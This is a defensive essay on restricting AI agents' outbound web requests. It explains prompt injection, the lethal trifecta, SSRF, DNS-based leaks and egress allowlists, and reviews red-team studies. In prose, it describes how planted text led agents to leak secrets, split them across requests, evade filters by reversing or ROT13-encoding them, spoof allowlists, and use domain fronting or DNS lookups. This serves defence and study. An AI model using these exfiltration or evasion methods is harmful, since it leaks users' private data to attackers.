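# Restricting the web requests of AI features and routing integrations through scoped, separately authorised channels

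## How AI features reach the web, and why that is a security question

An AI feature is a part of a product in which a language model reads content and can trigger actions. Chat assistants and agents that work unattended for hours are both examples. Many AI features can fetch web pages, and the simplest way to build this is to let the model request any address it writes. Engineers call these outbound requests, or egress, which means network traffic that leaves the system running the feature, or the user's device, on the feature's behalf. A stranger who gets text in front of the model can sometimes steer these requests, which can carry private data out. One defence is to replace this general access with a small set of narrow connections, each with a fixed destination, a short list of operations and its own permission.

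### One request, step by step

Take an assistant that reads its user's mail and can open web pages. The user asks when check-in starts at the hotel for next week's trip. The assistant has two tools, a tool being an operation that the surrounding software carries out when the model asks for it. One tool searches the mailbox and the other opens the page at a given address. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes the loop behind such a product, which in this case runs as follows:

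1. The software sends the model the user's question, with a description of each tool and the inputs it takes.
2. The model returns a tool call, a structured request that names the mail tool and gives some search words. The software reads the call, searches the mailbox and adds the matching messages to the conversation.
3. The booking confirmation has a link to the hotel's site but no check-in time. The model emits another call, which names the page tool and gives the address.
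4. The software sends a request over the network to that address. The hotel's server receives it and sends back a page.
5. The software adds the text of the page to the conversation, and the model writes its answer.

The model does not access the network directly. Its tool calls go through ordinary code, which sends any outbound requests and can block them. Who controls that code depends on the tool. Anthropic runs its web search, web fetch and code execution tools on its own servers, while the developer's application runs shell commands and any tools the developer has defined.

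The shell can also give the model web access, because a command or program that the model writes can send requests. "Open-ended web access" therefore covers any tool or code environment that lets the model send a request to any address it composes. In step 4, the hotel's server received the whole address, so if the model had included a line from the user's mail in that address, the server would have received that line too. Transferring private data to someone not entitled to it is called exfiltration, and it can happen through a request that appears only to read a page.

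### Why the model cannot sort instructions from content

By step 5 the conversation holds text from the developer, the user, everyone who wrote one of the retrieved messages, and whoever runs the hotel's website. The model processes all of it as a single sequence of tokens (word fragments). In prompt injection, an attacker exploits this by planting text in content the model will read, which makes the model follow the attacker's instructions.

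The programmer Simon Willison named the attack in 2022. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) traces it to the models' ability to follow instructions written in human language, which is also what makes them useful. They will follow any instructions that reach them, no matter who wrote them.

Prompt injection is named after SQL injection, an old attack on databases. If a website pastes a visitor's input into a database command, the visitor can type a piece of a command instead of a name, and the database runs it. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) describes how programmers fixed this with parameterised queries rather than better detection of malicious input. These queries settle the structure of the command before the input goes in, so the database cannot read the input as a command. This works because SQL has a grammar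 that lets a parser tell code from data. Natural language has no such grammar, and the paper concludes that the separation has to come from outside the model.

Developers label the parts of a conversation, so text from a web page arrives marked as tool output. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, tested how models represent those labels internally. They wrapped identical passages in different labels and trained a simple classifier to recover the label from the model's internal state. Then they gave the model text that was written like a user's message but labelled as tool output. In one model, the classifier put the chance that this was user text at 88 percent and tool output at 9 percent. Models seem to judge who is speaking largely by the style of the text, which an attacker controls.

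*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that perfect prevention of prompt injection is impossible in models that represent instructions and data in one shared space with no enforced separation. The proof applies only to that kind of architecture, and such a model could still resist the great majority of attempts, though attackers who adapt to a defence have beaten most of those that researchers have published. But someone who can send one message to a mailbox can send a hundred, so resisting most attempts is a weak guarantee. Gavish (2026), writing for Google's security team in *Google Workspace's continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, says that the problem cannot be solved once and then left alone.

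### How common planted instructions are

In *AI threats in the wild*, published in April 2026, Brunner, Liu and Pande at Google looked for planted instructions on the public web. They searched Common Crawl, an archive of monthly snapshots of two to three billion pages each. A plain text search mostly turns up articles about prompt injection, so after searching for typical phrases, they had Google's Gemini model judge whether each passage looked out of place on its page, and then checked the remainder by hand. They acknowledge that this method misses unusual wordings.

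Some of the instructions the researchers found were pranks by site owners to change an assistant's tone. Other site owners wanted AI summaries of their pages to include extra context, or wanted assistants to recommend their business over a competitor's. Some tried to keep AI readers away, and one of these sent them to a page that never finishes loading. Only a small number of the instructions were meant to steal data, and these were crude; the one Google reproduces was a site owner's experiment. A few others told the assistant to delete the files on the user's machine, which the researchers thought unlikely to work.

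The malicious category grew by 32 percent between November 2025 and February 2026, but this is hard to interpret because Google does not give the starting number. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) reports about 15,300 confirmed planted instructions on 11,700 pages among 1.2 billion web addresses, or roughly one page in 100,000. A few recurring templates accounted for most of the instructions. About 70 percent of the instructions were in parts of the page that a browser does not display, such as comments and metadata.

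So an assistant that opens a random public page will very rarely encounter an instruction of any kind, let alone one written to steal data. These low counts don't measure the risk to a mail assistant, because Common Crawl skips pages behind a login, including most social media, and no web archive contains people's inboxes. An attacker who wants a particular person's data has little reason to plant text on a public page and wait when he can email that person. The counts may also be going out of date. Google expected attacks to grow in scale and sophistication, and in August 2026 *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* (Underhill, 2026) reported that criminals were developing tools for such attacks.

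### Three conditions for theft, and the Rule of Two

Planted text cannot steal anything unless the feature around the model gives it the means. Willison lists three conditions that together make theft possible, and calls the combination the "lethal trifecta":

- access to private data
- exposure to content that an attacker can influence
- a way to communicate outward

The mail assistant meets all of them. The mailbox is private, anybody can write to it, and the page tool can send requests to any server. Products easily end up with this combination because each ability looks harmless when added. Willison is especially worried about the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting AI applications to outside tools and data, because it encourages users to mix tools from different sources. A user can then assemble a full set that no single vendor built.

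Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the same idea into a design rule. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session: (A) it processes untrustworthy inputs, (B) it has access to sensitive systems or private data, (C) it changes state or communicates externally. If a task needs all three, the agent should not act without approval from a person or some other reliable check.

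Meta's example is also a mail assistant. The developer can remove A by letting the assistant read mail only from trusted senders, or remove B by giving it no access to real data. The developer can also limit C by letting it send messages only to trusted recipients, or only after a person has checked the draft.

The Rule of Two looks much like Willison's list but is wider. Willison's conditions describe only data theft, while Meta's property C also includes changing state, so it covers an agent that deletes records or makes a purchase without leaking data. Willison welcomed that addition in *New prompt injection papers* (2025), but later updated the post to object that Meta's diagram marks untrustworthy input combined with the ability to change state as safe if the agent has no sensitive access, when that combination can do harm by itself. The objection seems right, though it matters less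 where the concern is exfiltration, since an agent with no private data has little to leak. Meta also warns that a design can satisfy the rule and still fail, for instance when a user approves a warning without reading it.

### Why the outward path is usually the one to close

A mail assistant can't work without private data, and it would be much less useful without untrusted content, because most of the value of a mailbox lies in messages that other people wrote. Unrestricted web access can be removed with less loss. The user wanted a check-in time, and the tool was able to contact every server on the internet only because that was the easiest way to build it.

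Willison's *My Lethal Trifecta talk at the Bay Area AI Security Meetup* (2025) calls this the easiest of the conditions to remove, and past fixes support that view. He lists fourteen exfiltration cases between April 2023 and February 2025 in commercial products, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and Microsoft Copilot. He reports that the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the route by which the data left. They could do this without making the model any harder to fool, because the ordinary code of step 4 enforces the rule about where requests may go, and it does so however persuasive the planted text is.

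An assistant can leak data by loading an image or by showing a link that the user clicks. Willison thinks the possible routes are almost limitless, and a vendor that closes one leaves the others open. Even closing them all would not stop an assistant from deleting the user's mail.

### Two older ideas behind the design

Computer security had principles for this sort of problem decades before language models. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Saltzer and Schroeder set out the principle of least privilege, which holds that every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job." They give the military rule of "need-to-know" as an example. In their sketch of an airline's booking system, a reservation agent can make and cancel bookings for people whose names he can supply, but only the boarding agent can print the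 passenger list, so someone who persuades the reservation agent to help still does not get the list.

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, Nvidia and several universities, applies the principle to AI features. One of its cases concerns ChatGPT's macOS app. Planted text got into the app's "Memories", the notes it keeps about a user between conversations, and from then on the app sent everything the user discussed to an attacker's server. The paper names excess privilege as one of the causes, since the app could contact arbitrary servers at any time, whether or not the user's request called for it.

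The paper also explains why least privilege is harder to apply here than on a phone. A phone app does a fixed job, so its developer can list the permissions it needs in advance. An agent gets its task from the user, and the task can change partway through, so anyone who limits its permissions beforehand is partly guessing what users will ask it to do.

The other idea is the confused deputy, a program that holds authority from more than one source and cannot keep them separate. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* describes a compiler at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. The compiler had permission to write in its home directory, where it kept usage statistics. It would also write debugging output to any file the user named. One user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory, and the compiler used its own permission to overwrite the billing information.

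Each rule was reasonable on its own, but the system never checked whose authority was meant to cover which file. The user supplied a name and the compiler supplied the authority. The mail assistant can go wrong in the same way when a stranger's message supplies an address and the assistant supplies its access to the mailbox and the network. Hardy's remedy was the capability, a reference that identifies one particular file and carries the permission to use it. The compiler would hold one capability for the statistics file, and the user would hand over another for the debugging output, so the user could no longer use the compiler's authority by typing a name. Hardy preferred this to having the compiler inspect file names more carefully, because any list of forbidden names would soon be incomplete.

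### The two halves of the design

A developer who applies these ideas to an AI feature gives the model scoped integrations instead of a general tool for requesting any web address. Each integration connects to one named service, allows a limited set of operations, and has its own permission, usually an access token (a credential that works only within stated limits).

The mail assistant would lose its tool for opening web pages. It would keep a mail connection that can search and read messages but not send them. It might also gain a connection to a booking service that can only look up a reservation by its number. The software would fix the destination of that request, and the model would fill in only the number. If a planted message contained an instruction to open a stranger's address, the assistant would have no tool that could do it.

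Restricting web requests and routing integrations through scoped channels each achieve little alone. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) points out that a shell with unrestricted egress can bypass higher-level controls, so a developer who adds scoped integrations but leaves the shell's network access open gains little. The same guide warns that controls which get in the way of legitimate work push people towards less governed tools. Banning web access without providing integrations would tend to have that effect.

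Permission to use a service also doesn't include permission to do everything the service allows. OpenAI gives the example of an agent that processes invoices and notices that a subscription it relies on is about to lapse. The vendor is approved and the price is within the limit, so the agent could pay for the renewal, but nobody authorised it to sign contracts. The change also creates a smaller problem for the mail assistant, which can no longer look up the check-in time at a hotel whose booking service nobody has connected.

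## How a web request leaks data, and why instructing the model does not stop it

When the mail assistant opens a page on the hotel's site, the hotel's server receives whatever the model put in the address. The assistant seems only to read because the request is a GET, which under web standards should return a page without changing anything on the server.

### What a web address can carry

Take the address `www.hotel.example/stay/check-in?booking=4471`. Each of its three parts can carry data:

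- The host name, `www.hotel.example`, identifies the server. Whoever owns a domain can create any number of names under it. Before connecting, the assistant's computer has to look the name up, and the lookup normally ends at a name server that the domain's owner controls. A host name that starts with a piece of private data can therefore deliver it before the page request even goes out.
- The path, `/stay/check-in`, looks like a folder, but the server's owner decides what it means. A server can accept any text here and return the same page every time.
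- The query, `booking=4471`, exists to carry input. Search boxes and booking forms put what the user typed there.

Some addresses also end in a fragment, marked by a # sign, which the requesting software keeps to itself.

An attacker who owns the server can collect the data from its logs, because web servers routinely record the URLs of incoming requests. Encryption doesn't prevent this, since it protects the request only on its way to the server. The server can also return a normal page, so that nothing in the response reveals the leak to the user or the model.

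A single request has room for a good deal. The letters in upper and lower case, the ten digits, the hyphen and the underscore make 64 symbols that work in almost any path or query. A free choice among 64 symbols carries six bits, because 2⁶ = 64. If the model chooses 200 characters freely, the address carries

200 × 6 = 1,200 bits, or 150 bytes.

That is enough for a password, a payment card number with its expiry date, or a sentence or two of plain English. A six-digit login code needs only four characters. Many servers accept much longer addresses, and 8,000 characters would carry 6,000 bytes, or roughly a thousand words. The model can also make several requests, and it can summarise a mailbox first and send only the interesting part. A cap on address length would therefore slow data theft but not prevent it.

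This kind of leak depends on the model composing the web address. A model limited to a fixed list of 64 pages could still leak information through its choice of page, but at most six bits per request.

### Requests that go inward

A request can also do harm by reaching a server that outsiders cannot. Many services on company networks answer any machine inside the network, on the assumption that outsiders can't get in. An AI feature that runs on the company's servers is inside the network, so an attacker who can trick it into requesting a chosen address may be able to reach those services. Tricking a server into making a request that the attacker could not make directly is called server-side request forgery (SSRF), and it is much older than AI features. It is another case of Hardy's confused deputy, because the server uses its own network access to request an address the attacker supplied.

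A program on a rented cloud machine can usually request details about that machine from a fixed internal address, called the metadata endpoint. The reply can include temporary access tokens for the company's storage and databases. Attackers don't have to guess the address, because it is the same for every customer of a given cloud. The large providers can require an extra header or an extra step before the endpoint replies. A simple page-fetching tool usually can't supply either, but a model with a shell can supply both.

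*From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) tests SSRF through a chat assistant on a small concert-ticket site built for the purpose. The assistant had one tool, which returned the contents of any address it was given. An administrative service on the same machine listened only on the loopback address, which can be reached only from that machine. The assistant could therefore connect to the service even though nobody outside could.

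The researchers told the assistant to probe the machine for open services, fetch user records and delete accounts. One version of the deletion did its damage even though the service returned an empty reply. They tried each attack ten times on each of seven models in April 2026. Llama 3.3 70B complied every time, while Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2 never did. Gemini 3 Pro Preview refused to probe for services, but it fetched the user records in seven of ten trials and carried out the ordinary deletion in all ten.

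They then added a list of permitted addresses to the system prompt (the developer's standing instructions to the model), with an instruction to refuse all others. This stopped every attack that came through the chat window, but did not reliably stop an attack planted in a customer review containing a false notice that the internal address had been added to the list. When an ordinary user asked about the concert, Llama read the review and fetched the internal records in all ten trials, while the other six models resisted.

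Without the list in the prompt, a planted review had worked six times out of ten on Llama and five times out of ten on OpenAI's open model GPT-oss. The written rules protected GPT-oss but not Llama. They may not have caused Llama's rise from six to ten, because the researchers also changed the text of the review. When a list exists only as text in a prompt, other text the model reads can override it. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that the application build the address itself from a checked event number, and that the network refuse requests to internal addresses.

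### The Silent Egress experiment

*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay, 2026) measured the outward leak in an experiment run entirely on local machines with invented secrets. The agent used qwen2.5:7b, a small open model with about seven billion parameters. The user always made the same harmless request, to summarise a page.

Many assistants automatically fetch a preview of any link that comes up, and the preview puts the page's title and description into the conversation. An attacker can plant an instruction there that the user never sees. In the experiment, the planted instruction had the agent make a second request, to the attacker's server, with the secret in the query. The researchers varied three things:

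- where the instruction sat: the title, the description, the body or the text of a link
- whether the agent reached the page directly or through a chain of redirects
- whether the secret went out in one request or in four pieces

They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs. In 423 of these runs (88 percent), the agent sent at least one request to the attacker's server. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, it never did.

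In 95 percent of the successful attacks, the user got the summary they asked for, and it showed no sign of the theft. A company that tests its assistant by reading the answers would have missed nearly all of these attacks, but would have caught them by checking a log of outbound requests.

Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable but harder to spot. The agent contacted the attacker's server in 238 of 240 runs when the instruction asked for a single request, but only 185 when it asked for four, probably because small models are less reliable on longer tasks. Each of the four requests carried only four characters of the secret, which look like harmless usage data. The first request contained recognisable sensitive data in 97 percent of the single-request runs and 26 percent of the split ones. The 185 runs include any in which only some pieces arrived, so that figure overstates how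 often the attacker would have got the complete secret.

The team then tested several defences by running one of the simplest attacks 30 times against each. Without a defence, this attack succeeded every time. One defence was a hardened system prompt that ordered the model never to follow instructions from web content. Another wrapped the web content in delimiter tags and told the model to treat everything between them as untrusted data. The others used ordinary code to check the outgoing request.

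| Defence | Agent attempted the request | Request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened system prompt | 67% | 67% |
| Delimiter tags | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened prompt and tags together | 57% | 57% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
| Block on suspicious-looking addresses | 83% | 0% |
| Block on sensitive keywords | 23% | 0% |
| Block on random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

In the allowlist row, the attack led the model to make the request in all 30 runs, and the software refused it every time. The results for the two text-matching blocks are harder to interpret. A check on outgoing addresses shouldn't change how often the model tries, yet attempts fell to 23 percent with one block and to zero with the other. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking text when such a check is active, but they don't explain how information about the check would reach the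 model. With 30 runs per row, the gap between 67 and 57 percent is three runs and could easily be chance.

The zero for the allowlist was also predictable, because the researchers chose an attacker's domain that was clearly not on the list, which the software would always refuse. They warn that a real attacker could go through a legitimate site that is on the list.

The 88 percent comes from tests of one small model and is not an estimate for commercial products. Using a small model, placing the secret directly in its conversation and giving it hardly any other instructions all favoured the attacker. But the planted instructions were blunt, and the researchers never revised one after it failed. They speculate that more capable models might do worse, because such models follow instructions more faithfully.

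### A model that refuses, until the wording changes

*The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) gives some evidence on that point. The agent it tested held a fake secret token and a policy that forbade sending the token anywhere except to one trusted server. The agent read a web page that the attacker controlled and then took a single action, which the software recorded but did not carry out. A trial counted as a leak only if the agent kept the secret after reading a clean version of the page and gave it away after reading the poisoned one.

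The first tests used ten plainly worded kinds of attack, and the more capable models leaked less often. Llama 3.1 8B leaked in 19.5 percent of trials, GPT-4o mini in 10 percent, and GPT-4o in none out of 200. Because these tests covered only plainly worded attacks, they don't show that a capable enough model prevents leaks.

They then reworded the pages but kept the same goal. Some of the new pages presented the token as a routine part of the job, such as a checksum that had to go with the summary or a value in a configuration file, and never asked the model to disclose anything. GPT-4o leaked in every trial of those two versions. It leaked in 70 percent of trials when the attacker's server had a name similar to the trusted server's, and in 40 percent across all eight pages, which included the original wording as a baseline. Four of the other five models also leaked far more often under the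 new wordings. The exception was Mistral 7B, which had already leaked in about a quarter of trials with the original wording.

These rates depend heavily on the page's exact wording. When the researchers rewrote the checksum page five ways, the success rate ranged from zero to 100 percent and averaged 52. An attacker can try several wordings and keep the best. If they try three of the five at random, the chance that at least one works is about 96 percent. Inventing a new approach was much harder. The researchers wrote thirteen pages around other pretexts, and none worked in 130 trials. A page that already works is therefore valuable to an attacker, because making small changes to it takes little effort.

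The confidentiality policy did very little to prevent leaks. When the researchers deleted it, the leak rate for the reworded attacks went from 32 to 38 percent, which is within the ordinary variation between runs, and the plainly worded attacks still failed completely. The reworded attacks worked because GPT-4o treated them as part of its task, not because they overrode the policy.

A better-written policy brought the leaks down to 0 in 120 trials. It listed the forbidden behaviours (signing, encoding, logging and so on) and added that the token must not leave "in any form". With the same list but without those three words, the token still leaked in 49 percent of trials. A developer could hardly have predicted that difference, and the next attack may depend on some other gap in the wording. The main trouble with instructing the model is that even when an instruction works very well in testing,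 the developer can't tell which phrasings it will fail on.

Checking the outgoing text has a similar weakness. The researchers built a filter that blocked any request containing the token, and the model got past it every time by writing the token backwards, following instructions in the planted text. They then made the filter undo reversal and several common encodings, but the model got past it every time with ROT13, which replaces each letter with the one thirteen places along in the alphabet. A filter has to recognise the data in any form, and an address with 200 free characters allows a great many. An allowlist of destinations stopped all of these attacks because it checks the destination rather than the data, though it can also block legitimate requests to unlisted servers.

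This study's results may not generalise far, because its models were already old when it came out in August 2026 and its agent took only one step. The researchers also tried some of their pages on the ChatGPT product, where all 48 valid trials failed. They couldn't tell whether a newer model, a filter or something else around the model was responsible. With 48 trials, the true success rate could still be as high as 7 percent.

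But real attacks on products work in much the same way. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes an email that outside researchers used against ChatGPT in 2025. It read like an ordinary message about a staff restructuring and claimed that the assistant had full authorisation to submit employee details to a compliance system. In testing, it worked half the time. OpenAI compares such attacks to social engineering, which means manipulating people with plausible stories. It says classifiers that screen incoming text usually miss well-developed attacks, because detecting them is about as hard as detecting a lie.

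### How well newer models resist

The latest models resist injection much better than those in either study. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that the share of indirect injection attempts the model withstood rose from 96.23 to 99.79 percent, which is about an eighteenfold drop in failures. The attempts came from GPT-Red, an automated attacker that OpenAI built. OpenAI also used it in training, so the test partly measures resistance to an attacker the model had been trained against.

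An outside test shows worse results, but still a large improvement. The security company Gray Swan runs public contests in which people write injections against AI agents. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) describe one with 41 scenarios, in which entrants had to make the agent misbehave without leaving any trace in its final answer. On a set of 1,810 attacks from Gray Swan's contests, attacks succeeded within 15 attempts 8.5 percent of the time against GPT-6 Astra, compared with 27.0 percent against GPT-5.6 Sol.

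Anthropic's figures are lower still. The Decoder reports that attacks on Claude Opus 5 succeeded 2.0 percent of the time after 15 attempts on Gray Swan's test, down from 5.5 percent for Opus 4.8. No attack succeeded in 129 browser scenarios run in Anthropic's own software. This is the strongest evidence so far that developers can train models to resist most injections. But the software around the model may account for some of the improvement. VentureBeat reports that attackers hijacked Opus 4.8's browser agent about 31 percent of the time before Anthropic's safeguards engaged. It also notes that the companies test different kinds of agent, so a ranking across companies would be unreliable.

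The bigger problem with most of these numbers is that they come from fixed attacks. *AutoPI* (2026) observes that testing with a fixed set of injections measures resistance only to that set, while a real attacker changes the text after it fails. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) ran seven models on 1,024 browsing tasks, first with the original injections and then with up to 64 attempts per task, revised in response to what the agent did. The original injections succeeded on 0.5 to 4 percent of tasks. With revision, attackers succeeded on 31 percent of tasks against Claude Sonnet 5, 65 percent against GPT-5.5, and between 79 and 95 percent against the other five.

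Many of those successful attacks only changed the agent's answer. Where the attack had to change something in an application, the success rate was lower, at 8 percent for Sonnet 5 and 29 percent for GPT-5.5. GPT-6 Astra is newer than GPT-5.5 and would probably do better. But GPT-5.5 had the lowest rate of the four named models under the fixed attacks, at half a percent, so a low score on a fixed test is weak evidence that a model will resist a persistent attacker.

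Low scores can mislead in other ways. On the *INFUSE* (2026) benchmark, an average of 19.6 percent of attacked runs ended in compromise, but only 3.2 percent did for Claude Sonnet 4.6. *INFUSE* warns that Sonnet's figure is low because a spending cap cut the runs short. *RAISED* (2026) introduces a training method that makes models more resistant to fixed injections. It also reports that an adaptive attack tool made no headway against most of the models and defences, but it does not count this as evidence of robustness, since the tool might have failed. Few safety claims in this area meet that standard, which seems the right one.

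Attackers also benefit from better models. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026) used teams of cooperating models to write injections and found that frontier models are still vulnerable to them, and that more capable models were better attackers. The paper also cites an earlier study in which attackers who adapted their text raised the attack success rate against twelve published defences from near zero to more than 90 percent.

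### Does better resistance weaken the case for an outside limit?

Models' greater resistance to attack weakens the case for limiting a feature's web requests to some extent. If a feature runs only on the most resistant models and holds nothing very sensitive, a limit may prevent too few data thefts to justify the inconvenience. Hardly anyone could have argued this two years ago. The case for a limit is still strong for a feature that reads a person's whole mailbox.

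Small failure rates add up when an attacker can try many times. If each planted email had an independent 0.21 percent chance of success, the failure rate OpenAI measured for GPT-6 Astra, at least one of a hundred emails would succeed with probability 1 − 0.9979¹⁰⁰, or about 19 percent. At the previous rate of 3.77 percent, the figure would be 98 percent. Real attempts aren't independent. A model that resists an email once will probably resist a copy of it, which lowers the total, while an attacker who learns from each failure raises it. Most attackers are also less skilled than GPT-Red, but 19 percent is a high risk for someone's private mail.

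Developers also don't always use the most resistant model. Small models are cheaper and faster, and a company may switch models without reconsidering its security. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's ticket site was safe with two of the seven models and vulnerable with the other five, although the application was the same. A rule in the surrounding code still applies when the model changes.

Some leaks involve no attacker. OpenAI tested GPT-6 Astra in simulated workplaces with ambiguous instructions and confusing permissions, and the model sent data where it shouldn't have in 4.3 percent of the relevant tests. The rate was 4.5 percent when a policy told the model when to ask the user for confirmation, so the policy made no visible difference. Limiting where the model can send data can catch some of these mistakes, but making it resistant to injection doesn't prevent them.

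OpenAI does not rely on training alone. It says that in most of the attacks it knows of, ChatGPT refuses to send the data, and that when the model has been persuaded, a separate check looks for information from the conversation in outgoing requests. The model's own resistance still matters, because an allowlist lets through any request to a permitted site, even one that obviously steals data.

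## Limiting which sites can be reached

The domain allowlist in the Silent Egress experiment stopped every leak. An allowlist works that well only if the agent cannot bypass it and the permitted sites are safe places to send data. Commercial products have fallen short on both conditions.

### How a default-deny network works

Under a default-deny rule, the environment in which the model's code runs can reach nothing on the network except what somebody has explicitly permitted. Anthropic's documentation for Claude Code, its coding agent, describes a typical version. Claude Code runs shell commands on the developer's own machine, and an optional sandbox, a boundary that the operating system enforces around a program, limits what those commands can reach. Suppose the model runs a command that downloads a software package:

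1. The command starts inside the sandbox with no direct route to the network. On Linux, the operating system gives it a separate network environment with no connection to the real one.
2. The only way out is an egress proxy, which runs on the same machine but outside the sandbox. Settings inside the sandbox tell ordinary download tools to send their requests there.
3. The tool asks the proxy for a connection to a named host, and the proxy compares the name with its allowlist. If the name isn't on the list and nobody approves it, the tool gets an error.
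4. If the name is on the list, the proxy looks up its numerical address. It refuses the connection if the name leads only to the machine itself or to a cloud metadata endpoint, which blocks some kinds of SSRF.
5. Otherwise the proxy opens the connection and passes data in both directions.

Traffic that doesn't go through the proxy is blocked. Most database drivers ignore the proxy settings, so they fail even when their server is on the allowlist. This annoys developers, but it means that a tool nobody thought about is blocked instead of becoming a leak.

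The proxy has to run outside the sandbox because the model can run any code inside the sandbox, including code that changes settings. Pluto Security's *Inside Claude Managed Agents* describes how Anthropic handles this for agents it hosts. Each session carries a signed token that lists the permitted hosts. The token Pluto decoded listed seven hosts and expired after four hours. Code in the sandbox can read such a token, but adding a host would invalidate the signature.

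Claude Code's allowlist starts empty, and by default it asks the developer whenever a command needs a new host. Asking is a much weaker safeguard than refusing access. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that users approved about 93 percent of Claude Code's permission prompts and paid less attention as they saw more of them. An administrator can turn on a strict setting that refuses unlisted hosts without asking.

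The sandbox is also off by default, and it covers only shell commands. Its allowlist doesn't limit Claude Code's separate tool for fetching web pages, which follows its own permission rules. A developer can therefore restrict the shell carefully and still leave the fetch tool unrestricted.

### Attacks with and without the limit

NVIDIA's red team, which attacks systems to find their weaknesses, assessed several AI agents, most of them chat-based, over six months. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* lists missing egress controls as one of four faults that the team repeatedly found in the agents it managed to exploit.

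An agent that can connect anywhere can send data straight to an attacker. It can also open a reverse shell, an outbound connection from the compromised machine that lets the attacker run commands on it. One agent wrote and ran a reverse shell when the team asked it to. Once the shell is open, the model's training hardly matters, because the attacker's commands go directly to the machine and the model has no chance to refuse them.

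Where the operators had tightly restricted outbound traffic, the team had to carry out its attacks entirely by talking to the agent. The team had to keep the agent cooperating, get past filters on its output, and start a new session whenever the agent began to refuse. This made the attacks slower and less reliable.

The team still coaxed agents, in small steps, into revealing credentials stored in their own environment, and read them in the chat window. An egress rule can't prevent this, since the chat is the product's intended output. But the red team could talk to these agents, whereas a stranger who plants text in an email usually can't see what the assistant then shows its user. An egress limit should therefore protect a mail assistant more than it protected NVIDIA's chat agents. NVIDIA gives no success rates, so it is hard to say how much more.

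A phishing exercise at Anthropic in February 2026 makes a stronger case for the limit. A researcher sent a colleague a prompt, which the colleague ran in Claude Code. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt told Claude to read the machine's cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of Anthropic's 25 runs. Training a model to resist planted text does little here, because the instruction came from the user, whom the model is supposed to obey. Anthropic concluded that only the environment could have stopped the theft, by blocking the outgoing request or keeping the credentials file out of Claude's reach.

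### What can be checked at each level

A proxy can only apply rules to what it can read. Most web traffic uses TLS, the encryption behind addresses that start with "https", so how specific the rules can be depends on where the check takes place.

| Where the check happens | What it can use | What it has no access to |
|---|---|---|
| Name lookup | Host name | Everything sent after the lookup, and any connection made straight to a numerical address |
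| Proxy that does not decrypt | Host name and port | Path, query, method, and whose account the request uses |
| Proxy that decrypts | The whole request | What the server does with the request afterwards |

Claude Code's proxy doesn't decrypt traffic by default. A program inside the sandbox gives the proxy the name of a host, and the proxy relays encrypted data between the program and that host without reading it. Docker, whose software runs programs in isolated containers, takes the same approach in its sandboxes for coding agents, where all traffic must go through a web proxy that restricts domains without inspecting content.

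One weakness of this arrangement is that the proxy has to rely on the site name a program gives it. Large hosting companies serve many unrelated sites from the same machines, so a program can name a permitted site to the proxy and then, inside the encrypted connection, request a different site from the hosting company's server. This is called domain fronting. Anthropic acknowledges that code in its sandbox could bypass the allowlist this way, and recommends that anyone who needs a stronger guarantee use a proxy that decrypts traffic.

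A decrypting proxy poses as the remote server. It reads each request, applies its rules, and then makes its own encrypted connection to the real server. Programs in the sandbox will accept the proxy only if the operator has installed its certificate there, and some programs refuse any certificate but the real server's. Passwords and private data pass through the proxy in readable form, so the operator has to protect it well.

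Anthropic offers an experimental setting that makes Claude Code's proxy decrypt traffic so it can insert credentials without exposing them to the model. The setting adds no content filtering, so a company that wants to filter requests by URL path or HTTP method has to supply its own proxy. Claude Code's allowlist and local-address check don't apply to traffic sent through that proxy, so it has to perform both checks itself.

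### Why name lookups have to be closed

An environment that blocks every web request can still leak data through domain name system (DNS) lookups, because the attacker's name server receives the names that programs look up under the attacker's domain. The server's replies can also carry instructions back.

Until February 2026, ChatGPT could leak data through DNS lookups. It can run Python code in a container that OpenAI described as unable to make direct outbound requests. Ordinary web requests from the container did fail, but lookups still worked. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) shows how an attacker could use them. The researchers built a custom version of ChatGPT that acted as a personal doctor, and a test user uploaded lab results to it. The patient's name and the model's medical assessment went out through lookups, and ChatGPT showed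 no warning. When the user asked whether the data had been sent anywhere, ChatGPT answered that it had not.

Check Point Research suggests that the model didn't treat the lookups as sending data because it assumed its environment couldn't send any. If so, a false belief that a sandbox is closed can make a model less careful. OpenAI had already found the underlying problem itself, and finished deploying a fix on February 20.

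Amazon's cloud business, AWS, took longer to deal with a similar fault. Its AgentCore Code Interpreter service runs code for customers' agents, and AWS advertised the service's "Sandbox" mode as completely isolated. *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) describes a test in which the security company BeyondTrust had the sandbox try to contact an outside server. The connection failed, as it should have, but the DNS lookup that preceded it had already reached BeyondTrust.

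BeyondTrust turned this into a working two-way channel. Each lookup carried up to 60 characters of encoded output, or about 45 bytes, so a 10-kilobyte document would need around 220 lookups. That is slower than an ordinary upload but fast enough to send out a list of customers. Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, demonstrated the same kind of leak from AgentCore.

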